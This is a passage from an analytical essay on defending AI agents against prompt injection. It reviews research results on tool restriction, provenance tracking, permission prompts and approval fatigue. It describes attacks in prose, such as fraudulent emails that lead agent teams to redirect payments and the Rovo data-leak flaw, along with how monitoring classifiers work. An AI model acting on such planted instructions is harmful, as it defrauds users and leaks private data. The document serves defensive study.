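An agent may also change its configuration during a session. For example, it could research a question on the open web, then lose its ability to communicate externally before it gains access to internal systems. The switch must be one-way, because restoring external communication after the agent has read private data would give it all three properties at once.

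### Criticism of the rule

Willison (2025), in *New prompt injection papers*, welcomed the rule because it also covers agents that change state, while the lethal trifecta covers only data theft. He soon added the reservation that Meta's diagram marked the combination of untrusted input and the power to change state as safe, even though an agent with both can do damage without seeing any private data.

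Meta changed the label to "lower risk". One of the people behind the rule explained that it is a minimum standard, and that the second property covers any system that matters to the user's security, even if it holds nothing private. A company's public social media account would count, for example, because a false announcement there could do serious harm. This answers the objection, but the rule's protection then depends on how well the developer identifies sensitive systems.

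Another criticism is that many of the most useful assistants need all three properties. For these assistants, the rule amounts to asking a person for approval, and that person may approve everything. Meta acknowledges that a compliant design can still fail, for example when a user blindly confirms a warning. Meta also says the rule doesn't address lesser harms such as misinformation in the agent's answer, which would include the slanted recommendation of a flat.

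The rule can also fail when several agents work together. *Taming AI Agents with seL4* (Alhindi, 2026) describes a team of five agents built to pay a small firm's suppliers. One read the suppliers' emails, others checked invoices, approved payments and sent them, and a coordinator managed the work and the bank's list of payees. Each agent obeyed the Rule of Two, but the agents passed text to one another, so words from a supplier's email could reach agents that had access to private records and the power to act.

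Alhindi tested the team with a fraudulent request to change a supplier's bank details. The request reached the coordinator in 23 of 40 runs, and the coordinator changed the account in 7 of those. No money went to the attacker during the test, but the next payment to that supplier would have gone to the wrong account. Alhindi then replaced the email agent with an ordinary program that extracted only the invoice number, order number, total and supplier. In 40 further runs, none of the planted text reached any agent.

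The team ran on GPT-4o mini, an old and small model, and a newer one would probably obey less often. But the paths between the agents would be the same, and a developer can find them before running anything by tracing which agents can pass text to which others. The repair works for invoices because the team needs only a few fixed fields. It wouldn't suit an agent that summarises customers' complaints, because that agent has to read what the customers wrote.

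### Choosing tools for each task

A developer can also give an agent only the tools the current task requires. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) tested an early form of this idea, called a tool filter. Before the model reads any outside content, it chooses the tools it will need based on the user's request, and it can't use any others afterwards. If the user asks for a summary of their email, the model selects the tool for reading messages but not the one for sending them.

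AgentDojo is a benchmark of 97 tasks in a simulated office, Slack workspace, travel agency and bank. Pairing the tasks with attackers' goals produces 629 security cases. On GPT-4o, the tool filter reduced attack success to 7.5%. Without a defence, versions of the same attack that addressed the user correctly succeeded in about 45% to 48% of cases. The filter did well because many tasks only required the agent to read something, while the attacker needed it to write or send something.

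*Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (2026) recalculated the results of several defences on 76 of the tasks. With no defence and no attack, the agent completed 67.1% of them.

| Defence | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed without an attack |
|---|---|---|
| Repeating the user's request after each tool call | 25.4% | 82.9% |
| Classifier that looks for planted instructions | 7.9% | 42.1% |
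| Tool filter | 6.5% | 69.7% |

The classifier and the tool filter stopped about the same share of attacks, but the agent completed 53 tasks with the tool filter and 32 with the classifier. The agent completed only two more tasks with the filter than with no defence, a difference that could easily be chance. Under attack, it completed 56.1% of tasks with the filter and 51.0% without it.

Restricting tools did better than filtering content in this comparison, but the classifier used for filtering appears to be the one from the 2024 tests. Newer detectors raise fewer false alarms, so a current classifier would probably cause far fewer tasks to fail.

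Debenedetti and colleagues describe several situations in which the tool filter fails. The agent may not know in advance which tools it needs, because the result of one step determines the next. A user may give several tasks in one session, so text planted during one task is still present when a later task adds a more powerful tool. In 17% of the security cases, the tools the task required were enough to carry out the attack. If all the attacks that still succeeded with the filter on came from those cases, attacks succeeded in about 44% of them, close to the rate without any defence. The filter would then have stopped nearly every attack that needed an extra tool and almost none of the others.

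### Enforcing the choice of tools

Alhindi's paper also tested tool restrictions on AgentDojo's banking and Slack tasks. seL4, an operating system kernel whose code is mathematically proved correct in certain configurations, blocked any call to a tool that the task didn't need. The prototype ran in a configuration that the proof doesn't cover. With GPT-4o mini, successful attacks fell from 48% to 7% of 249 cases, each run three times. The kernel blocked all 2,095 calls that the manipulated model tried to make to tools it didn't have.

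The share of tasks completed fell from 68% to 58% without an attack, and from 46% to 43% under attack. Alhindi reports that neither difference was statistically significant, but there were only 37 tasks without an attack, too few to rule out a real loss of ten percentage points. The model still saw a description of every tool, so it sometimes chose one that the kernel refused. Hiding the descriptions of tools the kernel would refuse might have prevented some of the failures.

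Alhindi then replaced the model with a script that carried out the attacker's instructions whenever it could. The kernel blocked 73% of these attacks, and the other 27% used only tools that the task required. The 73% figure is more useful for judging the restriction itself, because it doesn't depend on how easily the model is fooled. It is still a best case, since Alhindi took each task's tools from the benchmark's own solution, and a developer who had to guess which tools a task needs would probably allow more.

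Iyer and Babu (2026), in *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive*, propose a stricter rule that changes the available tools at every step. Their software keeps a set *s* of facts established so far. Each tool has a set *R* of facts it needs in order to run, and a risky tool also has a set *α* of authorisations. The agent sees a risky tool only if the tool is the next step on a suitable route to the user's goal and

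*R* ⊆ *s* and *α* ⊆ *s*,

which means that every required fact and every required authorisation is already in place. If a user asks the agent to answer a colleague's email about the budget, the tool for sending email stays hidden until a trusted step has confirmed the recipient. If the user only wants a summary, it never appears.

Iyer and Babu tested the rule on RiskGate, their own set of 182 simulated tasks, with 240 attacks for each method. The agent was a simple program that followed any planted instruction if the necessary tool was visible to it.

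| Tools the agent could see | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|
| All of about 100 | 100% |
| The ten that best matched the request | 100% |
| Those it could run at that moment | 75% |
| Those needed for the next step | 25% |
| Those needed for the next step, with authorisation for risky ones | 0% |

The agent completed every task under all five methods. When Iyer and Babu put seven real language models in control, the last two rates were the same for each model.

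The zero follows almost directly from the design, since an agent can't call a tool that the software has withheld. The perfect completion rate isn't very informative either, because tasks that every method completes are too easy to show how much the restriction hinders the agent. Iyer and Babu wrote the tasks and the attacks themselves, and they say the main thing missing is testing on independent benchmarks such as AgentDojo.

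The rule failed when planted text could forge an authorisation, and attacks again succeeded 25% of the time. The protection therefore depends on accepting authorisations only from the user or a trusted check, never from the content of an email or web page.

Benchmarks of this kind may also be too easy. Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025) found in *Indirect Prompt Injections* that a simple check between the agent and its tools reached the lowest possible attack rate on four public benchmarks, including AgentDojo. Once a simple defence gets a perfect score, a benchmark can't show whether a more elaborate defence is better.

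### Permission for a tool and permission for an action

Withholding the payment tool stops an agent from making any payments, but an agent that needs the tool for a task can still use it to pay the wrong person. In Alhindi's experiment, every attack that still succeeded used only tools that the task needed. In about half of those attacks, the agent had the payment tool to pay a bill and used it to send money to the attacker.

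Mellafe Zuvic (2026) argues in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* that developers often confuse letting an agent see a tool with authorising a particular call to it. Mellafe Zuvic examined the public code of LangChain/LangGraph, LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which developers use to build agents. All three let a developer choose which tools an agent can see, but by default none of them checks whether the values in a call, such as the account or the amount, are authorised before the tool runs. Developers can add this check if they know they need it.

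Mellafe Zuvic's check, ScopeGate, compares each tool call with rules the company wrote in advance. The tool and the account must be approved, and the amount must be below a ceiling. ScopeGate refuses the call if any of these checks fails or the software hits an error. It refused all 48 prepared attempts to get around it and all 29 unauthorised calls from an attacker that adapted over 40 rounds. It allowed all ten legitimate calls, but with so few, the true rate of wrongful refusals could be as high as about 26%, at 95% confidence.

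The objection is right, but it isn't a reason to stop withholding tools. Withholding blocked 73% of the attacks by Alhindi's script without anyone having to decide which recipients were legitimate. Blocking the rest requires a second check, on values such as the recipient.

ScopeGate's approach suits a company that pays the same suppliers every month. It works less well for a personal assistant, because no administrator can list in advance everyone the user might want to pay.

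### Tracking where a value came from

CaMeL, a 2025 design from Google DeepMind, avoids the need for such a list. A trusted model writes a plan using only the user's request, before outside content can influence it. Other software then carries out the plan and tracks where each value came from. As Alhindi summarises it, a rule can then refuse a payment if the recipient's details came from an email. The model doesn't have to recognise that the email is malicious.

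*ToolFence* (2026) applies a similar idea to individual recipients. If the user asks the agent to pay Alice, the agent gets permission to pay only Alice. If planted text leads the agent to propose paying a stranger, the software blocks the payment, and the agent goes on to pay Alice.

The broadest test of this approach is in *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026). Just before each tool call runs, their software records where the call's values came from and works out what the call would change. It then compares those changes with what the user's request authorised. Text that the model writes can't extend the authorisation.

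The researchers tested PACE on eight benchmarks with models from three families. It had the lowest attack success rate in 62 of 79 comparisons and tied for the lowest in another 14. Compared with an undefended agent, it reduced the share of tasks completed by at most three percentage points on any full benchmark. In a small adaptive test, none of 30 attacks achieved a goal the user had not authorised, though the true success rate could still be as high as about 10%.

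These are strong results, and the loss of useful work is small. But the researchers proved their security guarantees for a stricter version than the one they tested, so the proofs and the measured completion rates apply to different systems. The tested version can restore a call that one of its two checks has blocked if the other check finds that the user authorised it, which probably helps the agent complete more tasks.

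Tracking values interferes with some tasks more than others. Suppose a user asks an agent to pay a plumber's invoice that arrived by email. The account number has to come from the email, so a rule against sending money to account numbers found in emails would block the payment the user wanted. The software could ask the user to confirm the number, or compare it with one from an earlier payment. A fraudulent invoice from an unfamiliar company would still be hard to tell from a real one.

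A payment can be unauthorised even if the recipient and amount are correct. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026), a guide for companies, describes an agent that processes invoices and notices that the company's subscription to a document-signing service is about to end. The agent tries to renew it so that it can keep working. The supplier and the price may both be within its limits, but nobody asked it to commit the company to a new contract. OpenAI recommends tying the agent's authority to its task and requiring separate approval for new commitments. This works if ordinary code can recognise a new commitment, for example because the payment matches no approved invoice. If a model has to decide what counts as a new commitment, the company is again relying on a form of content filtering.

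### Atlassian Rovo

Rovo is an AI assistant for companies that use Atlassian's workplace software, such as the project tracker Jira. It can also read connected services, including Slack and Microsoft 365. *Researchers Uncover RovoBlast Vulnerability in Atlassian AI Assistant* (Mascellino, 2026) reported in August 2026 that a click on a malicious link could make Rovo disclose company data through its web research agent. Varonis, which had also found SearchLeak, reported the flaw to Atlassian, which fixed it.

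Rovo is a hard case for session-wide restrictions because data could leave through one of its ordinary features. Its research agent could read internal documents and use the open web in the same run, which broke the Rule of Two without any unusual configuration. An administrator who had carefully reviewed the connected services could still have overlooked this route. Administrators also can't remove Rovo completely from an Atlassian system.

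Varonis advised companies to disconnect services they don't use and prevent Rovo from accessing legal, financial and personnel files. It also recommended turning off browsing agents and multi-step automation for teams that don't rely on them. The advice is sensible, but it requires administrators to find every part of the product that can access the web, and to check again whenever Atlassian adds a feature.

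Lockdown Mode creates similar work for the administrators of managed workspaces, who have to review each connected app themselves and remember that the mode doesn't cover Codex. OpenAI's guide advises companies to test capabilities both individually and in combination, and to keep new actions off until someone has reviewed them. Companies that make assistants could take on much of this work by publishing a list of every feature that can send data out and the setting that controls it. They could also make restricted modes block new features by default, so that if an administrator misses an update, a feature stays unavailable instead of opening a new route for data to leave.

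## What users lose and how they respond

Benchmarks measure how many tasks an agent completes, which leaves out much of what users lose under a restriction. An assistant that displays no links can still answer a question correctly and pass the test, but the user can't easily check the answer. Benchmarks also don't measure how many people tire of a restriction and turn it off.

### The cost of each restriction

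What users lose depends on what they use an assistant for. *When Should I Trust This?* (Warren, Eser and colleagues, 2026) reports a May 2025 survey of 1,000 American adults who used AI at least once a month. The most common uses were research and recommendations (49.9%), writing and editing (38.6%), and ideas and inspiration (35.2%). Someone who wants a letter rewritten loses almost nothing if the assistant can't open web pages, show pictures or make payments. People doing research lose more, because they need current information and sources they can inspect.

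Without live browsing, an assistant has to rely on stored pages or on what the model learned in training. *Synthetic Sources?* (2026), an audit of four AI search engines, warns that answers from a model's internal knowledge may be outdated or invented. The user may not notice, because an old visa rule, for example, looks like a current one. A product could show the date of each stored page so the user knows when to check elsewhere.

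Users notice the loss of images or payments more easily because the task stops. An assistant that can't show pictures is little help to someone choosing a sofa by its looks. One that can't pay can still fill a basket, and the user usually loses only a minute or two at the checkout. But it can't buy a concert ticket that goes on sale while the user is asleep.

The cost of losing links is harder to judge, because it depends on whether people would have opened them.

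### How often people open an assistant's sources

Browsing records suggest that people check answers much less than they say they do. In Warren and colleagues' survey, 94.7% said they verified answers some of the time, and another 1.4% said they always did. Pew Research Center's *Google users are less likely to click on links* analysed what 900 American adults did online in March 2025. When Google showed an AI summary above its search results, people clicked a source in the summary on 1% of visits.

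Other studies found higher rates. Ding, Facciani and colleagues (2025), in *Citations and Trust in LLM Generated Answers*, let people ask a chatbot their own questions and tracked whether they used the mouse to check its citations. Ouyang and Narechania (2026), in *Analyzing the Presentation, Content, and Utilization of References*, asked 12 students to judge answers from nine assistants. In *Fostering Appropriate Reliance on Large Language Models* (2025), 308 people each answered eight factual questions with help from an AI that was wrong half the time and gave sources with half of its answers. Reeves (2026), in *Unreliable AI answers are ‘good enough’ for most users of platforms*, reports on a UK survey that asked people what they would do.

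| Source | Measure | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Pew Research Center | Visits in which people clicked a source in Google's AI summary | 1% |
| Ding and colleagues | Answers with citations that people checked | 9.8% |
| Ouyang and Narechania | Click rate for ChatGPT's references, the highest of the nine assistants | About 12% |
| *Fostering Appropriate Reliance on Large Language Models* | Answers with sources where people opened at least one | 26% |
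| Reeves | ChatGPT users who said they would click at least one media link | 26% |

The studies count different things, and participants in an experiment may check more than they would at home. The Google figure also includes many quick searches with little to check. Even so, all the measured rates are far below the rates people report for themselves.

People varied widely around the averages. In the experiment with 308 participants, 189 never opened a source, while 45 opened at least one every time they could. People also use links for reasons other than checking. Reuters Institute's *Emerging uses of AI chatbots for news* (2026) found that 51% of those who click through from a chatbot to a news site do so to get more detail. But chatbot users were more likely than users of search engines or social media to say they clicked to verify the news or learn about its source.

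Assistants often give users no source to open. In *Signals, Evidence, and Context*, Biswas and Lin (2026) studied 368,644 exchanges in which a user replied to an answer that could be checked. The assistant invoked research, experts or another authority in 31.9% of these answers but gave a web address in only 1.33%. The conversations date from 2025 or earlier, and the records may not have kept every source, so current products probably link more often than these figures suggest.

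In 28.7% of those exchanges, the user questioned or disputed the answer in the chat. This is a poor way to catch a manipulated assistant, because the same assistant responds to the challenge. In *The Decision to Verify* (2026), 87% of participants used at least one fact-checking tool, but some relied on the chatbot that had given them the information.

### Whether sources help people catch errors

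*Fostering Appropriate Reliance on Large Language Models* also recorded how often participants gave the right final answer:

| Sources | When the AI was wrong | When the AI was right |
|---|---|---|
| None offered | 19.5% | 72.7% |
| Offered but not opened | 24.2% | 74.8% |
| Opened | 37.0% | 81.7% |

People who opened sources did better, but they may have been more careful to begin with. Comparing answers with and without sources is fairer, because the researchers assigned these at random. When the AI was wrong, offering sources raised the share of correct final answers from 19.5% to about 27.5%. The researchers chose questions that most people get wrong and asked participants not to search elsewhere, so the effect in ordinary use could be quite different.

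Sources can also mislead people who don't open them. When the AI gave a wrong answer without an explanation, adding sources raised participants' average confidence from 4.92 to 5.43 on a seven-point scale. Ding and colleagues found that citations made people trust an answer more, even when the citations were taken at random from other people's questions.

People check an AI's answers more usefully when the product shows them where the AI is uncertain. *Not All Uncertainty Is Equal* (2026) compared several ways of marking uncertainty. With one method, people clicked links for 20.4% of wrong answers and 11.8% of right ones. Without any marking, their checking did not differ significantly between right and wrong answers.

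### What this implies for removing links

Removing every link would make little difference to most readers on most days, since they wouldn't have opened one. It would hurt the minority who check, probably on the answers they most doubt. Readers would also lose a warning sign, because they can't learn anything from missing sources if an assistant never shows any. In the experiment with 308 participants, 29 said they had gone against the AI when it gave no sources.

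A product without links could instead quote the relevant passages. Irons, Cooper and colleagues (2026), in *To Believe or Not To Believe*, asked 162 people to judge AI answers about science articles, 70% of which were correct. Each person had one kind of help:

| Help available | Correct judgements | Average time | AI answers accepted |
|---|---|---|---|
| The full article | 85.7% | 45.8 seconds | 71.5% |
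| Three passages chosen by search software | 83.1% | 33.0 seconds | 64.7% |
| An explanation written by an AI | 80.8% | 25.4 seconds | 86.5% |

The differences in overall accuracy were small enough to be due to chance. But people who read the AI's explanation accepted far too many answers and caught fewer of the wrong ones. Passages worked almost as well as the full article and saved time, although the article may be better for checking answers that summarise several points.

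Quoted passages suit a restricted assistant because ordinary software can copy them from the page. A manipulated model can't reword them, and the user has no link to click. But if an attacker wrote the page, the passage may repeat the false claim, and the reader can't look around the site for signs that something is wrong. Linking only to pages that the software has retrieved would still let readers do that. Given how much some readers benefit from links, limiting links this way seems better than removing them.

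### How people respond to browser warnings

The best field evidence on how people handle confirmations comes from browser warnings, which appear when a site looks dangerous. *Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) analysed more than 25 million warnings shown by Firefox and Chrome. They concerned malware, phishing or SSL, the technology that encrypts a connection to a website.

| Warning | Share that users clicked past |
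|---|---|
| Malware and phishing, Firefox | About 10% |
| Malware and phishing, Chrome | About 25% |
| SSL, Firefox | About 33% |
| SSL, Chrome | 70.2% |

Akhawe and Felt concluded that warnings can work, and the malware and phishing figures support that conclusion. Browsers show malware and phishing warnings mainly for sites already reported as dangerous, so these warnings are rare and usually right. SSL warnings often result from harmless mistakes by a site's owner, which probably taught many people to ignore them.

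Design also affects whether users heed warnings. Chrome's users clicked past SSL warnings about twice as often as Firefox's did. Google later redesigned Chrome's SSL warning to make the safe choice more prominent, and the share of users who heeded it rose from 37% to 62%. But Malkin and Egelman (2018), in *An Experience Sampling Study of User Reactions to Browser Warnings*, noted that many people still seemed not to understand the warnings after such improvements.

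Familiarity may make people less careful. Almuhimedi, Felt and colleagues found in *Your Reputation Precedes You* that Chrome users clicked past a fifth of malware warnings on average and heeded warnings more consistently for sites they had not visited before. An agent's requests often concern services the user knows well, such as their own email account.

According to CRN's *Google Chrome Users May Suffer From Attack Warning Fatigue*, Akhawe and Felt advised designers to limit the number of warnings people see. This is hard to do when an agent needs permission for each step of a long task.

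### How often people approve an agent's requests

The most detailed figures come from Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, which used to ask by default before it ran most commands or changed files. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reported that users approved 93% of these requests and described "approval fatigue", in which people stop paying close attention to what they approve. By August 2026 the approval rate was 97%, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026).

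Most of the requests were probably harmless, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that users are careless. They did reject 39% of the plans Claude presented for whole tasks.

Stronger evidence comes from an experiment in which Anthropic had a research company give coding work to 1,053 paid testers. Partway through, the company replaced the text of one permission request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests.

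The testers were not working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than real users. Anthropic also published the result to justify replacing these requests with another system. But low stakes can't easily explain why the testers caught fewer commands later on, since the stakes didn't change. Habit is a likely explanation, though the testers who reached 50 requests may have been the ones who clicked quickly from the start.

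The replacement, auto mode, applies content filtering to the agent's actions, using a classifier to judge each one. It blocked 89% of the same dangerous commands and let 116 through. The testers had rejected only six of those 116, so a human check after the classifier would have added very little, unless people paid more attention because they saw fewer requests.

Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes themselves. Its *Running auto mode in production* describes an engineer, Kai, who uses auto mode for all his coding but returns to manual review when the work affects other teams. If an agent asks for confirmation only in cases like these, the user has a reason to read each request.

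A sandbox can also reduce the number of permission requests, without a model to judge them. Claude Code's sandbox limits which files and websites a command can reach, and commands that stay within those limits run without permission. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) reported that this reduced permission requests by 84% in the company's internal use. Other users may see a smaller reduction, because someone has to configure the sandbox for each new capability, which Anthropic calls "high-maintenance".

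### One attack in 24 years

An example with invented figures shows why approval becomes a habit. Suppose an agent asks its user for 40 confirmations a week, and one request in 50,000 results from an attack. The user answers 2,080 requests a year, so they face an attack about once every 24 years. Approving without reading is the right response to all but one of those 50,000 requests, and the user gets almost no practice at recognising an attack.

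At 20 seconds a request, careful reading would also take the user about 278 hours for each attack they met. That is worthwhile only if the attack would do serious harm.

The company that makes the agent has more reason to worry. A million such users would face about 41,600 attacks a year. If they rejected 13.6% of these, as the testers in Anthropic's experiment did, nearly 36,000 would succeed.

If a sandbox removes 84% of the requests but every attack still produces one, the user sees about six requests a week, and one in 8,000 comes from an attack. The user still meets an attack once in 24 years, but reading the requests carefully takes about 44 hours per attack instead of 278. The sandbox helps more if it blocks some attacks outright, because then the user doesn't have to notice them.

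### How people avoid restrictions

Some users turn off the confirmations. Anthropic reported that 25% of interactive Claude Code sessions started in a mode that skips permission checks. As of June 2026, 49.5% of command-line users of Claude Code had created a rule that automatically approves certain commands, and many of these rules were broad enough to allow almost anything. Gusto, one of Anthropic's customers, adopted auto mode because constant requests were leading its engineers to bypass the checks entirely.

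Programmers know how to change such settings, so these figures may overstate how often other people would do so. No similar figures appear to exist for optional protections in consumer chatbots. OpenAI has not published how many people use Lockdown Mode or how often they switch it off for a single chat. Allowing users to switch it off for one chat is probably safer than only allowing them to turn it off completely, because they might forget to turn it back on.

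People can also take a blocked task to a less restricted product. Nobody seems to have measured how often this happens, but the temptation is clear. Anthropic says that business customers who use auto mode, which interrupts them less, complete about 25% more code changes, although people who chose it may already have been more productive.

The remaining workaround is to move data by hand. If an assistant can't open a private link to a lease, the user can download the lease and paste its text into the chat. This is safer than letting the model open any address, because the user decides what to share. But any instructions planted in the text still reach the model, and under a rule like Anthropic's, links in the text may count as the user's own. If the user pastes the lease into a different assistant, the first assistant's restrictions don't protect it.

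A developer can allow exceptions to a restriction without letting the model grant them. Anthropic says auto mode is designed never to approve sending code or secrets to an outside destination. A user who wants to send them has to switch modes or run the command themselves. A manipulated model would then have to persuade the user to take one of those steps, which is harder than getting them to click "approve" on one more request.

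### Strict defaults or optional strict modes

Companies disagree about whether strict protections should apply to everyone or only to people who choose them. The argument for strict defaults is that users can't easily judge their own risk. Text planted on a public web page can reach anyone whose agent reads it, including people who have never heard of prompt injection and wouldn't look for a setting. A manipulated agent can also harm others, for instance by writing to the user's colleagues. Anthropic made auto mode the default partly because it believed many users were approving requests by reflex. In October 2026, it announced that the default would extend to most Claude apps.

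The argument for optional modes is that strict protections limit what everyone can do, while some of the most serious attacks target only a few people. OpenAI argues that some users may be comfortable with the risks of connected features and should be able to choose. Someone planning a holiday gains little from restrictions meant for an executive with confidential files. If the restrictions apply anyway, that person may turn them off or switch to another product, and so also lose the protections that didn't inconvenience them.

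How an optional strict mode compares with a milder default depends largely on how concentrated the risk is. Suppose 2% of users turn on a strict mode that prevents 90% of thefts against them, while a milder default would prevent 50% of thefts against everyone who leaves it on. If thefts are spread evenly across users, the strict mode prevents only 1.8% of all thefts, and the default prevents 50%. But if half of all thefts target the 2% who chose the strict mode, it prevents 45%. If a quarter of users switched the default off, it would prevent only 37.5%, less than the strict mode in that case.

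No company has published the figures needed to make this calculation for a real product. The answer probably differs between restrictions. Few people would bother to turn off a block on outside images in a chat about their email, so it makes sense as a default. Far more people would look for a way around a ban on live browsing. OpenAI roughly follows this division. Its check on web addresses is part of the ordinary product, while the much more restrictive Lockdown Mode is optional. OpenAI describes its general aim as "transparent controls and strong defaults", which allows for both.
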